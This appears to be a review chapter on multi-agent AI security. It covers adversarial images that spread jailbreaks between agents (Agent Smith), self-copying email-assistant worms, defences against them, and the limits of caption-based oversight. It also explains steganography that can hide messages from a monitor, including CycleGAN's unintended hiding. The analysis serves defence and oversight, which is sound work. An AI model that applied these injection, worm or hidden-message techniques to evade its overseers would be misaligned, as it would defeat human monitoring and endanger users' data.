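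Simpler clean-up methods had almost no effect in the same study. Area scaling, which worked well for Quiring and colleagues, only reduced the success rate from 68% to 67%. The hidden text was designed to survive averaging, unlike the T in the earlier example. Median filtering, blurring, compression and random masking did no better.

Trail of Bits' most important recommendation is to require the user's explicit confirmation before text in an image can trigger a sensitive action. This would have given the Gemini CLI user a chance to stop the email with the calendar data, though it doesn't remove the mismatch.

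## Agent Smith: an image that spreads from one agent to the next

In the Ghostcommit attack, a malicious image was passed once, to a coding agent. If agents also store the images they receive and send them on, one altered image can reach agents that the attacker never contacted. *Agent Smith* (Gu, Zheng and colleagues, 2024) demonstrated this in simulations of up to a million agents. The experiment used small models that are now old, but its mathematics is still useful for estimating how good a check between agents has to be.

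### How the image spread

Each simulated agent ran on a vision-language model, usually LLaVA-1.5. It had a role, a record of its last three exchanges and an album of up to 10 images. In each round, the software split the agents at random into questioners and answerers and paired them. The questioner planned what to talk about, retrieved the image in its album that best matched the plan, and sent it to the answerer with a question. The answerer replied and saved the image in its own album. Once an album was full, each new image replaced the oldest one.

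The researchers altered an ordinary picture so that it matched almost any plan. An agent with the picture in its album therefore nearly always retrieved it and sent it to its next partner, which stored it and later did the same. The picture also made the models produce harmful text the researchers had chosen in advance. The attacker only had to place the picture in the first album.

In a test with 256 agents, the researchers put the picture in one agent's album. By round 8, 23% of the agents had produced the harmful text at least once. The share rose to 94% by round 16 and over 99% by round 24. An attacker who compromised one agent per round would have reached only an eighth of them after 32 rounds.

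In the million-agent run, the researchers put the picture in 1,024 albums at the start to save computing time, and it reached almost all the agents before round 32. The paper's opening figure describes this run as starting from a single agent, which contradicts the experimental section. Only the runs with 256 and 1,024 agents started from one album, so the claim that one image can reach a million agents is an extrapolation, though a plausible one within the simulation. By the paper's own formula, a million-agent run starting from one album would take at least 14 more rounds.

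A person would have had trouble spotting the altered picture. In one version, the researchers changed each colour value by at most 8 or 16 steps on the scale from 0 to 255, and in another they changed only a border six or eight pixels wide. OCR wouldn't have helped, because the picture didn't need written words. When the researchers tried a picture with written instructions instead, it infected no agents.

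An overseer who read only the agents' conversations could also have missed the problem. When the attack used a border of only four pixels, the picture sometimes kept spreading quickly even though most agents that carried it didn't produce the exact harmful text.

### The spread as an equation

Gu and colleagues describe the spread with an equation like those used for infectious diseases. Let *c* be the share of agents that carry the picture. The *infection rate*, β, is the chance that a questioner who carries the picture passes it to an answerer who doesn't. The *recovery rate*, γ, is the chance that a carrier loses the picture in a given round, for example because newer images push it out of the album. The share of carriers then changes at this rate:

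dc/dt = βc(1 − c)/2 − γc

The first term counts new carriers. A pair has a carrier as questioner and a clean agent as answerer with probability c(1 − c), and the picture passes between them with probability β. The product is divided by two because there are half as many pairs as agents. The second term counts the carriers that lose the picture.

If β is greater than 2γ, the share of carriers settles at 1 − 2γ/β, however few agents carried the picture at the start. Otherwise, the picture eventually dies out.

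Suppose β is 0.4 and γ is 0.1. The share of carriers settles at 1 − 0.2/0.4, or one half, so 500 agents in a system of 1,000 would carry the picture. In each round, about 50 clean agents would receive it and about 50 carriers would lose it.

### How much a filter has to block

Gu and colleagues' equation can be used to calculate what share of infected images a filter would have to block in transit for the image to die out, though they didn't test such a filter. Blocking a share *f* reduces the infection rate from β to (1 − f)β. The image dies out if (1 − f)β is no more than 2γ, so *f* has to be at least 1 − 2γ/β. In the example, the filter has to block half of the infected images.

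Blocking exactly half brings the system only to the threshold, where the picture disappears very slowly. The table shows the equation's predictions for a filter switched on when half the agents already carry the picture.

| Infected images blocked | Infection rate with the filter | Final share of carriers | Rounds until only 1% carry the picture |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0.4 | 50% | Never |
| 25% | 0.3 | 33% | Never |
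| 50% | 0.2 | 0% | About 980 |
| 75% | 0.1 | 0% | About 70 |
| 100% | 0 | 0% | About 39 |

Agent Smith's own settings would require a much better filter. Each agent receives an image in about half of the rounds, so an album that holds 10 images drops each one after roughly 20 rounds. This makes γ about 0.05. If the infected image is passed on in nearly every chat, β is close to 1 and the filter has to block about 90% of infected images. The true figure could be higher, because an agent that receives the infected image again keeps it for longer.

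The calculation also assumes that the filter has an independent chance of catching the picture at each hand-over. In practice, the agents pass on the same file, so a detector that misses it once will probably keep missing it. A more realistic model may be a filter that always catches the picture but protects only some of the agents. The threshold is the same, so in the example half of the agents need the filter.

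Once someone finds the picture, the overseer can add its cryptographic hash to a blocklist so that every agent can refuse it, since all the copies are identical. This stops working if a program re-saves the picture, because that changes the hash. Software could also count how many agents hold the same file and flag one that suddenly appears on many agents, although this would also flag a new company logo.

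An organisation could also raise the recovery rate by clearing its agents' image memories more often. In the example, doubling γ to 0.2 would also bring the system to the threshold. But a smaller memory doesn't always help. In one of Gu and colleagues' tests, the share of agents producing the harmful text in round 16 was 54% with albums of two images, 88% with albums of six and 78% with albums of 10. A medium-sized album probably keeps the picture long enough to spread while containing fewer harmless images that the agent might retrieve instead.

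The researchers tried cleaning images in transit by randomly resizing, flipping and compressing them. The picture still reached about 90% of the agents when they designed it to survive these changes and altered it more heavily.

### Defences tested on 128 agents

Gu and colleagues left open how to design a practical defence. *Cowpox* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) proposes one that needs to run on only a few agents. When a protected agent detects suspicious output, it makes a harmless "cure" image that other agents are more likely to retrieve than the malicious one. The cure then spreads through the system the same way as the attack.

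In a typical test, Wu and colleagues used Cowpox to protect four of 128 agents. The share of infected agents peaked at 74% and fell to 3% by round 50, when it would have been 94% without the defence. But about 90% of the agents had been infected at some point, so Cowpox is better at ending an outbreak than at preventing one. If an infected agent had already sent an email or deleted a file, its recovery would not undo that.

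In *Catching the Infection Before It Spreads* (May 2026), Ma, Yang and Zhang present a defence that tries to find the picture before an agent passes it on. They also object that Cowpox makes the agents' conversations more alike, because the agents keep retrieving the cure.

In this method, each agent first holds practice conversations with itself, playing several characters with different names and personalities. A healthy agent's characters retrieve different images and talk about different things, while an infected agent's characters keep retrieving the same image and producing similar text. The software treats an agent as infected only if both the images and the text show unusually little variety.

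The software then looks for the malicious image. If the agent's conversations have changed abruptly since the last check, the infection is probably recent, so it deletes the newest image. Otherwise it splits the album in half and repeats the test on each half, continuing with any half that seems infected until three or fewer images remain. It deletes all of these, usually removing one or two harmless images along with the malicious one.

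The main tests began with four infected agents out of 128 and ran for 64 rounds. Without a defence, every agent became infected at some point. With the new method, the worst result was seven infected agents (5.47%). In most tests the figure was zero, because the method removed the picture from the first four agents before they could pass it on. The next table gives the highest share of agents infected at the same time for each model in one version of the attack.

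| Model | No defence | Cowpox | Ma and colleagues' method |
|---|---|---|---|
| LLaVA-1.5-7B | 100% | 40.62% | 0% |
| InternVL2-8B | 92.19% | 74.22% | 0% |
| InstructBLIP-7B | 92.19% | 74.22% | 0% |
| Qwen2-VL-7B | 90.62% | 82.81% | 0% |

The paper gives the same infection figures for InternVL2 and InstructBLIP in every column, to two decimal places. Two different models are unlikely to match so closely, so this may be a copying error. The results for the other two models don't depend on these figures.

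The method's false alarms are a bigger concern. In a separate test with 800 agents, it detected 95.4% of the infected agents and wrongly flagged 6.8% of the healthy ones. If those rates applied to 128 agents of which four were infected, one check of the whole system would flag about four infected agents and eight healthy ones. The paper reports a precision of about 86%, meaning that most flagged agents really were infected, but infections were far more common in that test. (The text gives the infected share as 70%, while the reported accuracy and precision fit a share of 30%.)

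A false alarm deletes a harmless image from the agent's memory. In another test, the method removed 97.7% of the malicious images but kept only 80.6% of the harmless ones. That loss may be acceptable for agents that chat about pictures, but not for an agent whose album holds the only copies of a customer's documents. Moving suspicious images to a separate folder would be safer than deleting them.

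The practice conversations also take time. The standard check uses four characters and takes twice as long as a check with one. A check with eight takes four times as long and detects nearly all infected agents, but still wrongly flags 5.5% of healthy agents. Ma and colleagues suggest running the checks while agents are idle.

They argue that an attacker would struggle to evade the method, because a picture that agents retrieve constantly is bound to make their conversations less varied. They don't report testing it against an attacker who tries. The epidemic equation suggests a possible weakness, because a picture can spread without being passed on in every chat. With an infection rate of 0.4 and a recovery rate of 0.1, it would still reach half the agents, and the conversations might remain varied enough to pass the check.

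### Worms in email assistants

A *worm* is a malicious program that copies itself from one computer to another. In *Here Comes The AI Worm*, Cohen, Bitton and Nassi (2024) built a version that spreads between AI email assistants through messages. Unlike Agent Smith's picture, it follows the connections between people who write to each other.

The first version of their paper includes an attack that uses an attached image and works even if nobody opens it. The researchers wrote their own email assistant, which used LLaVA to decide whether to forward a message, reply to it or treat it as spam. It correctly classified a real advertisement as spam. After the researchers altered the picture attached to the advertisement, the assistant classified the message as one to forward and chose which of the user's contacts should receive it. If those contacts used the same assistant, it would forward the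 message again.

A later version of the paper focuses on text. As with EchoLeak, the attack begins with an email that the assistant later retrieves as background material. Here, the email makes the assistant copy the malicious instructions into its next message, along with private information from the user's other emails. In the tests, about one in five assistant-generated emails compromised another assistant. *Here Comes the AI Worm* (Cohen, 2025), the conference version, reports that each compromised assistant compromised 20 others within one to three days.

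*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* points out that the leaked information went to the next people in the chain, and not necessarily back to the attacker. The experiments ran on the researchers' own machines, so they show that such a worm is possible, but not that one has spread through public email.

Cohen and colleagues also tested a defence that compares what goes into the model with what comes out. A self-copying instruction has to appear in both, so a close match is a warning sign. The check caught every worm in the main test and wrongly flagged 1.5% of harmless cases. Like the search for repetitive conversations, it looks for something the attack needs in order to spread, so it doesn't have to recognise particular wording. It would be less useful for images, because an agent that forwards a harmless photograph also sends exactly what it received.

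### How far the results carry over to current agents

None of these image experiments used a model released in 2025 or 2026. The models that Ma and colleagues tested in 2026 date from 2023 and 2024, and the largest has about eight billion parameters, far fewer than leading models are likely to have. All the image attacks described here also took place in laboratories. The results therefore can't show how easily an image would spread among the agents that companies use today.

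The attacker in Agent Smith also had an unusual amount of information. The researchers designed the picture using the same model and image-retrieval software as the agents, along with 512 records of earlier conversations. They also tested a mixed system, with half the agents running on LLaVA and half on InstructBLIP, and the picture infected almost all the agents of both kinds. But they had designed that picture using both models, so the test doesn't show whether it would infect agents running a model the attacker couldn't study.

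An attacker can get this information for a model whose weights are public, but not normally for one that a company keeps on its own servers. The attacker can instead design the picture on public models and hope that it also works on the target. Wang, Ying and colleagues (2025) had some success with this approach in *Manipulating Multimodal Agents via Cross-Modal Prompt Injection*, combining altered images with malicious text. However, they attacked individual agents, and a picture that has to spread must work on one agent after another.

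Using the same model everywhere is probably the most realistic part of the experiment. A company may well run hundreds of agents on one model because that is cheaper and easier to manage, and an image that works on one agent is then likely to work on the rest. Using several models would make the attack harder, though the mixed test suggests that two may not be enough if the attacker can study both.

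Random pairing is less realistic. In the simulation, any agent could meet any other, and every chat included an image from the questioner's album. Most office agents work in fixed sequences, and many have no reason to send a stored picture to anyone. That would lower the infection rate, and a picture might never leave the team where it started. But one agent that prepares slides for every department could spread a picture faster than random chats would. The equation doesn't capture these differences because it treats all agents as equally connected. If an overseer can check only a few agents, those that send images to the most others are the best ones to check first.

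More recent papers cover spread through text. *AgentWorm* (2026) describes self-copying prompts that spread between agents in OpenClaw, an ecosystem of long-running agents with broad access to their computers. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* (2026) describes worms that cross from one agent platform to another. It also finds that letting an agent read a file can be more dangerous than letting it write one, although security rules often treat reading as the safer permission. An agent with read-only access to a shared folder of images could still pick up a malicious image and pass it on in its next message.

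## Caption-based review: checking a description instead of the image

In caption-based review, the overseer reads a description of an image instead of looking at it. This might suit a system like the one in the Agent Smith experiments, where agents exchange more pictures than anyone could open. Captions can work well for broad questions, such as whether a picture shows a weapon. They are much less suitable for finding leaked data, embedded instructions or hidden messages, because these often depend on details that a description leaves out.

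### Why a reviewer might prefer text

People create 4 billion images a week with ChatGPT, the coding agent Codex and OpenAI's programming interface, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Images 2.6* (2026). Staff could look at only a tiny fraction of these. A caption takes seconds to read, and a company can store and search captions. If it learns in March that its agents have been drawing an unreleased product, it can search the captions from January and February instead of reopening every image. An auditor can also see what the reviewer read before approving an image.

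Captions also let reviewers use text filters for names, account numbers or threats. A language model's safety training may work better on words than on pictures.

Checking a caption instead of the image saves money only when a company reuses the caption for later checks. A vision-language model has to process the image to write the caption, so the first check may cost about as much as asking the model directly whether the image is acceptable. Stored captions can also leak data. If a caption repeats a customer's name from a chart, that name ends up in the database.

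### How ECSO replaces an image with a caption

Adding an image to a prompt can make a chatbot's safety training less effective. *Eyes Closed, Safety On* (Gou, Chen and colleagues, 2024) tested five models on 1,110 harmful questions, each paired with a harmless picture that the model didn't need. Four of the models gave harmless answers only about 20% of the time with the picture, while all five did so almost every time without it.

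The models could still recognise harm when asked about it. The researchers collected 500 safe and 500 unsafe answers, and two of the models classified more than 95% of them correctly. The researchers' method, ECSO, uses this ability in four steps:

1. The model answers the user's question with the image, as usual.
2. The same model judges whether its answer is harmful. If it finds no harm, the user receives the answer.
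3. Otherwise, the model writes a caption of the image with the user's question in mind.
4. The model answers again from the question and the caption, without the image, and with an instruction to be harmless and ethical.

A harmful request written inside the picture becomes ordinary text in the caption, and the model is then more likely to refuse it.

The main test used MM-SafetyBench, a collection of requests whose harmful part is mostly in the picture. ECSO raised LLaVA-1.5-7B's average share of harmless answers from 48.1% to 90.3% for pictures of written words, from 48.8% to 86.4% for generated pictures with a line of text added, and from 85.0% to 95.4% for generated pictures without words, which were less effective attacks. The paper prints starting averages of 31.7% and 32.1% for the first two, but these match neither its results for the eight kinds of harm nor the improvements it reports.

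The instruction in the fourth step probably contributed to the improvement along with the captions, because the model gave harmless answers to only 81.9% of the same requests in plain text. Removing the image also helped. When Gou and colleagues supplied the image along with the caption, the share of harmless answers to the 1,110 questions fell from 91.8% to 85.6%.

The models rarely misjudged their answers to ordinary questions as harmful. When they did, the user still received an answer based on the caption. The error rate ranged from 0% to 4.6%, depending on the model and the test. Captions written for the question worked slightly better than general ones. For a question about two elephants, for example, a general caption left out their positions and led to a wrong answer, while a caption written for the question included them.

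Gou and colleagues left out five of the benchmark's 13 kinds of harm because even text-only models handled them poorly. A caption can't help if the model reading it doesn't recognise the problem. ECSO is only partly caption-based, because the model is still given the image in the first two steps. It controls how a model answers a user, and the researchers didn't test it on images made by an agent.

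### Later comparisons of captions and images

*When Helpers Become Hazards* (2026), a benchmark of dangers in daily life, found little of this benefit. On 400 test cases, replacing images with captions did not improve two of the three models and improved the third by only about 4.75%. Some of the risks were in small visual details that captions usually missed. This probably explains much of the difference from ECSO's tests, where the harmful part was often a line of writing or the question itself, which is easier to put into words.

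*SafeCap* (2026) tries to improve the captions through reinforcement learning. One model answers after seeing the image, another answers after reading only the caption, and a judge checks whether the two answers agree about safety. They also count as agreeing if both models overlook a risk and neither gives harmful advice. A high score therefore shows that the caption preserved the first model's judgement, which may be wrong.

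For a coarse decision, captions can be nearly as good as images. *Teaching Vision-Language Models to Decline* (2026) used a judge model to decide whether another model had answered a question about an unsuitable image when it should have declined. The same judge ran first with captions and then with the images. The two versions agreed on 98% of cases in a test of 1,500. In a larger test, they disagreed on 255 of 12,000 cases, and the caption version found slightly more failures for every model configuration. The judge needed to know only roughly what each picture showed and did not need to read small text, and the task was not about safety.

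Content moderation from captions has gone less well. In *Benchmarking System One Models in Online Moderation* (2026), the model Laya reached about 66% accuracy in one set-up, whichever of three models wrote the captions. In another set-up, it caught about 96% of unsafe items but was right only about half the time overall, because it flagged too many safe ones. If half the items were unsafe, it would have flagged roughly 94% of the safe ones. The benchmark's published results for other systems can't show how much the captions reduced accuracy, because those systems received different inputs.

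No published experiment from 2025 or 2026 seems to compare caption-based review with direct image review on the charts, screenshots or documents that agents make. Researchers could run one by planting customer names and instructions in some files and leaving others clean. The same model would then review every file twice, once from a caption and once from the image, and the researchers would count its misses and false alarms.

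### How much of an image fits into a caption

A colour image of 1,024 by 1,024 pixels stores 3,145,728 colour values (1,024 × 1,024 × 3). Software can hide one bit in each value by making the value even or odd, which changes it by at most one step. The image can therefore hide about 393,000 characters of plain text, at eight bits per character.

A model writes a caption in *tokens*, which are words or pieces of words from a fixed vocabulary. If the vocabulary has 130,000 tokens, a caption of 100 tokens can hold at most:

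100 × log₂(130,000) ≈ 1,700 bits

Writing out the hidden message would take about 1,850 captions of that length. Real captions hold much less information than the maximum because language is predictable. For instance, the word "chart" adds almost no information after "a bar" in a description of sales figures.

By this calculation, a caption could still report that an image contains a hidden message, since a yes or no takes only one bit. But a captioner is unlikely to notice colour changes of one step, and the tests that look for them need the exact pixel values.

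A caption can omit leaked data even when it has room for it. A customer's name takes only a few tokens, but the accurate caption "A bar chart of quarterly sales by region, with the north highest" leaves out the name printed on the northern bar. Nothing directs the captioner to include the name unless someone has asked about names.

If the captioner leaves something out, the overseer can't recover it by studying the caption. This follows from the *data-processing inequality*, a theorem of information theory that processing data can't add information about whatever produced the data. If a captioner works only from the image, its caption can't contain more information about a hidden message than the image does, and no analysis of the caption can contain more than the caption. A second model that reads the caption may guess that the chart has customer names on it, but it can't check this without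 the image.

The theorem limits how much information a caption can hold, but not how easily a model can use that information. ECSO's captions held less information than the pictures, but the models responded to them more safely.

### How often models misread images

A caption can also be wrong. *Humanity's First Exam* (Kelly, Kementsietsidis and colleagues, 2026) tested 18 models on 544 questions that people find easy, arranged in groups of four closely related versions. One question asks how many of the coffee mugs at the front of a group have no steam rising from them. Another asks for the colour of the third letter in each word of a neon sign.

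The five best models answered 96% to 98% of the questions correctly on a single try. Their average fell to 85.8% when they had to be right consistently across repeated runs and related versions. A correct caption for one chart is therefore weak evidence that the same captioner will get a similar chart right.

Errors in visual perception accounted for 73% of the wrong answers. That share depends partly on how many questions involved images, but Kelly and colleagues found that extra reasoning helped much less with perception than with text and symbols. A captioner that misreads a label may therefore keep misreading it however long it reasons. The error rates are probably higher than they would be for ordinary pictures, because the researchers kept only starting questions that at least one of five models had got wrong at least once.

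Harder tests show larger gaps in the skills needed to read charts. On *HumanSightBench* (2026), the best model scored 45.3% at recognising text content. Before an update added GPT-6 Astra, all eight models failed the same 61.8% of the counting questions in all three runs. Most business charts are easier to read, but reading a crowded dashboard may require both skills.

A second captioner catches fewer of these mistakes than one might expect. *Humanity's Sixth Sense* (2026) classified 8,573 failures by 24 models on tasks of intuitive visual reasoning. The two most common causes were missing a decisive visual cue (21%) and misidentifying an object, person or role (20%). Among tasks that at least five models failed, the median share of a task's failures with the same cause was 80%. Two captions that agree may therefore contain the same error, even if they come from different companies' models.

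### When the captioner is misled or has a stake in the answer

Text in an image can target the captioner as well as a downstream agent. A line in pale type might instruct the captioner to leave out a suspicious footnote, and if the captioner complied, the overseer would see nothing suspicious in the caption. Models often ignore such instructions, but an attacker who has studied the captioner's model might be able to control the caption without written words, using an altered picture like the one in Agent Smith.

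If the captioner copies an embedded instruction word for word, the model that reviews the caption receives it as text, and models are more likely to obey instructions in text than in images. Neither the captioner nor the reviewing model should therefore have tools that could send data or change files. The reviewing model's verdict can still be wrong, so ordinary software should also search the caption for instructions before that model reads it.

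The captioner normally receives only the picture, without its metadata, source code or hidden parts. Even an accurate caption of the Northern Ireland police table would have missed the staff records on the other worksheet. If software resizes the image after the captioner has processed it, the caption may describe a different version from the one the next agent receives.

Often the easiest caption to get is one the agent has already written, such as in its message to the user. The reviewer is then relying on the agent's own account of its work. If the agent didn't realise that a chart contained private data, it probably won't mention the data in the caption, just as Cyberhaven's agents usually didn't mention the leaked material to the simulated user. If the agent has obeyed an embedded instruction, that instruction could also control what it writes about the result.

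A separate captioner that hasn't seen the agent's description avoids this dependence, and the overseer can compare its caption with the agent's description. If the agent describes the file as "a summary of the workbook" but the captioner describes a login button, as it might have for Logue's Copilot diagram, someone should open the file.

### OpenAI's checks on generated images

For its image generators, OpenAI checks images directly instead of relying on captions. According to OpenAI's *ChatGPT Images 2.5 System Card*, a language model first checks the text of the request. A second model, which can process images, then checks all the text and pictures that go into the generator. The second model also checks the finished image, and the user sees the image only if it passes. The previous version, ChatGPT Images 2.0, used the same kind of monitor.

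OpenAI tested the whole system with prompts designed to produce images that break its rules. With one of the two new generators, GPT-Image-2.5-Sunburst, 77.0% of the prompts led to a safe image, the system blocked 21.9%, and 1.09% led to an unsafe image that a user would have seen. That last rate was 1.41% with the other new generator and 1.64% with the previous version. Neither new generator's rate was statistically significantly different from the previous version's.

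The 1.09% figure makes the blocking look more reliable than it was, because most prompts never led to an unsafe image. The table's last column gives the unsafe images shown as a share of blocked prompts plus unsafe images shown.

| Type of harm | Blocked | Unsafe image shown | Share missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| All types | 21.9% | 1.09% | 4.7% |
| Sexual | 89.1% | 0.52% | 0.6% |
| Violence and gore | 16.3% | 0.64% | 3.8% |
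| Self-harm | 22.3% | 1.13% | 4.8% |
| Abuse | 25.4% | 1.69% | 6.2% |
| Violent and nonviolent wrongdoing | 10.2% | 2.86% | 21.9% |

The system missed fewer than 1% of the sexual cases but more than a fifth of those involving wrongdoing, possibly because a picture of wrongdoing can look ordinary unless someone reads what it explains. The blocked cases include requests that OpenAI refused before generating an image, so the table doesn't show how well the final image check works alone. An automated grader assigned the labels and may have made mistakes. The rates don't apply to ordinary use, where few prompts are designed to break the rules.

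These checks target sexual content, hate, violence, extremism, self-harm, political content, abuse and similar harms. OpenAI reports no rate for confidential data, instructions aimed at another agent or hidden messages. The sales chart with a customer's name on one bar breaks none of the rules in the table, so passing such a check would be little evidence that it is safe to publish.

The design is still useful to an overseer because the monitor receives both the request and the image. An overseer could give a similar monitor the agent's task, the finished chart and the recipients' names, and ask it whether sharing the chart fits privacy norms. That question worked best for photographs in MPCI-Bench, but a monitor for charts would need its own test.

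OpenAI also tested whether its image generators could answer questions about biology and cybersecurity. It instructed them to write their reasoning and a final answer in an image, then graded the answer. A caption such as "a page of handwritten notes" would have left out the reasoning and the answer, which a reviewer would need to check.

### Questions, OCR and close-up views

If an overseer does use captions, specific questions can recover some of what a general description omits. For the sales chart, the overseer could ask the captioner:

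- Which people, companies or accounts does the image name?
- What exactly do the title, labels and footnotes say?
- Does any text address a reader other than the sales director?
- Is there a link, a QR code or a button?

*MLLM-as-a-Judge for Image Safety without Human Labeling* (2025) applies this idea to safety rules. Its method, CLUE, breaks a rule into the conditions an image must meet to violate it, and uses a model to check those conditions instead of the whole rule. CLUE also compares the model's scores for the whole image and for a copy without the central region. This comparison raised the share of unsafe images detected from 90.5% to 91.2%. Its bigger benefit was to reduce the average number of longer reasoning steps per image from 1.32 to 1.16.

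Questions help only with problems the overseer has thought of, and some, such as whether a bar represents a single customer, can't be answered from the picture.

OCR is better than a caption for exact wording, because a captioner may shorten "Excludes Harlow Foods, contract under dispute" to "a footnote". The overseer can also compare the OCR output with the caption and inspect the image more closely if, for example, OCR finds 40 words that the caption doesn't mention. But an image may still contain instructions that OCR misses, as DeepKeep's tests with tilted text showed.

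Software can also cut the image into regions, enlarge each one and have the captioner describe them separately. This makes small print easier to read and gives a faint footnote in the corner its own description. The regions should overlap so that a word split in one appears whole in another. The overseer still needs a description of the whole image, since the legend that explains a bar may be in another region. With 16 regions and 100 tokens for each, the captions can hold at most about 27,000 bits, less than 1% of the hidden message in the earlier example. Describing each region can therefore recover visible details, but not a message spread across the pixel values.

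Looking at an image more closely doesn't guarantee a correct reading. Artificial Analysis' *VIALS-AA* (2026) gave models 161 tasks with scientific images and tools for enlarging, cropping and measuring them. In one task, the models had to locate a faint protein spot and read its weight range from a scale. GPT-6 Astra answered correctly after enlarging the picture fourfold, as did Claude Sonnet 5.5 after cropping the area, increasing the contrast and measuring the spot's position. Grok 4.7 viewed the image 20 times but gave the wrong range, apparently because it used the printed label beside the spot instead of the spot.

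The best model got 64% of the tasks right in all three runs. Claude Sonnet 5.5 and GPT-6.1 Sol scored 60% and 59%, although Sonnet used tools 3.6 times as often. The cost per task ranged from $0.02 to $1.77. Even at $0.02 each, inspecting 4 billion images a week would cost $80 million. Most images are simpler than these scientific ones and would probably cost less to inspect, but a company may still want to closely inspect only images that will leave the organisation or go to an agent with access to private data.

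## CycleGAN and the detection of messages hidden in images

Even a careful caption leaves out details too faint to see, and an AI system can put such details into an image without being asked. *CycleGAN, a Master of Steganography* (Chu, Zhmoginov and Sandler, 2017) reports that a neural network trained to turn aerial photographs into maps hid parts of the photographs in the maps.

### How photographs ended up inside maps

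CycleGAN is a method for training two networks together. Here, one turned aerial photographs into maps, and the other turned maps into aerial photographs. The researchers trained them on about 1,000 photographs and 1,000 maps. Training rewarded maps that a third network classified as real. It also rewarded the two networks for accurately reconstructing a photograph from the map made from it.

An ordinary map doesn't contain enough information to reconstruct the original photograph. Many photographs fit the same map, differing only in details such as roof colours and tree positions. Yet the second network restored these details almost perfectly. One photograph showed a white roof with a pattern of black dots. The roof was plain grey on the map, but the dots reappeared in the right places in the reconstruction. The same thing happened with nearly every photograph the researchers tried.

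Chu and colleagues increased the local contrast of a generated map and found a fine pattern in areas that had looked plain. A real map treated in the same way had no such pattern. Adding random noise of about three steps on the scale from 0 to 255 to the generated maps was enough to ruin the reconstruction, and so was saving the map as a JPEG. Smoother noise, which changed neighbouring pixels together, did little harm, so most of the hidden information was in tiny differences between neighbouring pixels.

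In another test, the researchers edited a tree into a photograph of a field, first in one place and then in another, and recorded how each edit changed the map. When they added both changes to the original map, the second network produced a photograph with both trees. They could also alter almost any map imperceptibly so that the second network produced a photograph of their choice.

None of this required an intention to deceive. Training adjusts a network's numerical settings in small steps that improve its score. If a map happened to contain a faint trace of the photograph, the reconstruction would be slightly better, so training would strengthen both the trace and the second network's response to it. A visible trace would have made the map look less real to the judge, which presumably kept the pattern faint. As training went on, the second network responded to ever smaller changes.

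The finding matters most for developers who train several models together and let them pass images to each other. The clue was that the reconstruction was too good for what the map visibly showed, and looking at the maps alone would not have revealed the problem. A developer can check for hidden information by adding slight noise to the images that pass between two models. If the second model then does much worse, it was probably relying on something invisible. Chu and colleagues also suggest giving the map an extra channel that could store the information openly, but they had not yet tested this.

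### The prisoners' problem

The cryptographer Gustavus Simmons described the basic situation in 1983 as the *prisoners' problem*. Two prisoners, usually called Alice and Bob, want to plan an escape. They may write to each other, but a warden reads every letter and will separate them at the first sign of a secret. Encryption alone doesn't help, because scrambled text would alert the warden. They need letters that look ordinary but contain a message that only the other prisoner can recover, usually with a key they agreed on beforehand.

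In CycleGAN, the network that generated the maps had the role of Alice, the network that reconstructed the photographs had the role of Bob, and the judge had the role of the warden. The judge failed to stop the messages even though it was trained throughout to tell generated maps from real ones. With AI agents, the overseer is the warden. The overseer can defeat the scheme without reading a message, because showing that one exists is enough to start an investigation.

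Watermarking uses similar techniques to embed authorised signals. Guan, Arosemena and colleagues (2026) point out in *Toward Accountable AI-Generated Content on Social Platforms* that watermarking is designed mainly to survive attempts at removal, whereas steganography is designed mainly to go unnoticed.

### Hiding three bits in three pixels

The simplest way to hide a message in an image is to replace each colour value's *least significant bit*, its last binary digit, with a bit of the message. This makes the value even or odd, as in the caption calculation. The table shows how three grey pixels can hold the bits 1, 1 and 0.

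| Original value | In binary | Bit to hide | New value |
|---|---|---|---|
| 200 | 11001000 | 1 | 201 |
| 201 | 11001001 | 1 | 201 |
| 57 | 00111001 | 0 | 56 |

The recipient reads the new values as odd, odd and even, which gives 1, 1, 0. The second pixel already had the right last bit, so it stayed the same. On average, hiding a message changes half of the pixels used for it.

These invisible changes leave a statistical trace. The method can turn 200 into 201 and 201 into 200, but it never turns 201 into 202. Suppose an innocent image has 1,000 pixels with the value 200 and 600 with the value 201. An encrypted message has about as many ones as zeros, so if it fills all these pixels, about 800 will end up with each value. A detector can look for pairs of neighbouring values whose counts are suspiciously equal.

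### Cachin's measure of security

In 1998 the cryptographer Christian Cachin proposed a way to measure how much a hiding method gives away. It uses *relative entropy*, which measures how far one probability distribution is from another. If C is the distribution of innocent covers and S is the distribution of images with messages, the measure is:

D(C‖S) = Σ C(x) × log₂(C(x) / S(x))

The sum runs over every possible image *x*. The same formula works for a single pixel. In the example, an innocent pixel from the pair has the value 200 with probability 0.625 and 201 with probability 0.375. After the message goes in, both probabilities are 0.5:

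0.625 × log₂(0.625 / 0.5) + 0.375 × log₂(0.375 / 0.5) ≈ 0.046 bits

That is very little evidence from one pixel, but it adds up. If the 1,600 pixels are independent, the total is about 73 bits.

Cachin showed that if the relative entropy for the whole image is ε bits, a detector that never raises a false alarm must miss at least a fraction 2^−ε of the messages. At 0.1 bits, it must miss at least 93% of them. At 73 bits, the formula sets practically no limit on how well a detector can do.

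If the relative entropy is zero, innocent and altered images have exactly the same distribution. Wang and Moulin (2007), in *Perfectly Secure Steganography*, call such schemes perfectly secure because no statistical test can reliably detect the message, so better software wouldn't help an overseer.

Nobody can calculate the measure exactly for photographs, because nobody knows the true distribution of innocent photographs. Both the sender and the overseer have to estimate it from examples.

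### The square-root law

According to the *square-root law*, the length of message that a sender can hide in an image at a given risk of detection grows with the square root of the number of pixels. *Information-Theoretic Limits for Steganography in Multimedia* (2021) gives the example that a cover four times as large can hide only twice as many bits at the same risk.

Suppose an image of one million pixels can hide 1,000 bits at an acceptable risk:

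| Pixels | Bits hidden at the same risk | Bits per 1,000 pixels |
|---|---|---|
| 1 million | 1,000 | 1 |
| 4 million | 2,000 | 0.5 |
| 100 million | 10,000 | 0.1 |

The reason is that chance variation grows more slowly than the image does. If a detector counts a feature found in half of all pixels in images without hidden messages, the count typically varies by chance by about 500 in a million pixels and about 1,000 in four million. If each hidden bit shifts the count by the same small amount, the larger image can hide twice as many bits.

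The same reasoning applies to a series of images. An agent that sends 100 pictures of equal size can hide only about ten times as much as it could in one, at the same overall risk of detection. An overseer who keeps all of an agent's images and analyses them together therefore has an advantage over one who checks each image and then discards it.

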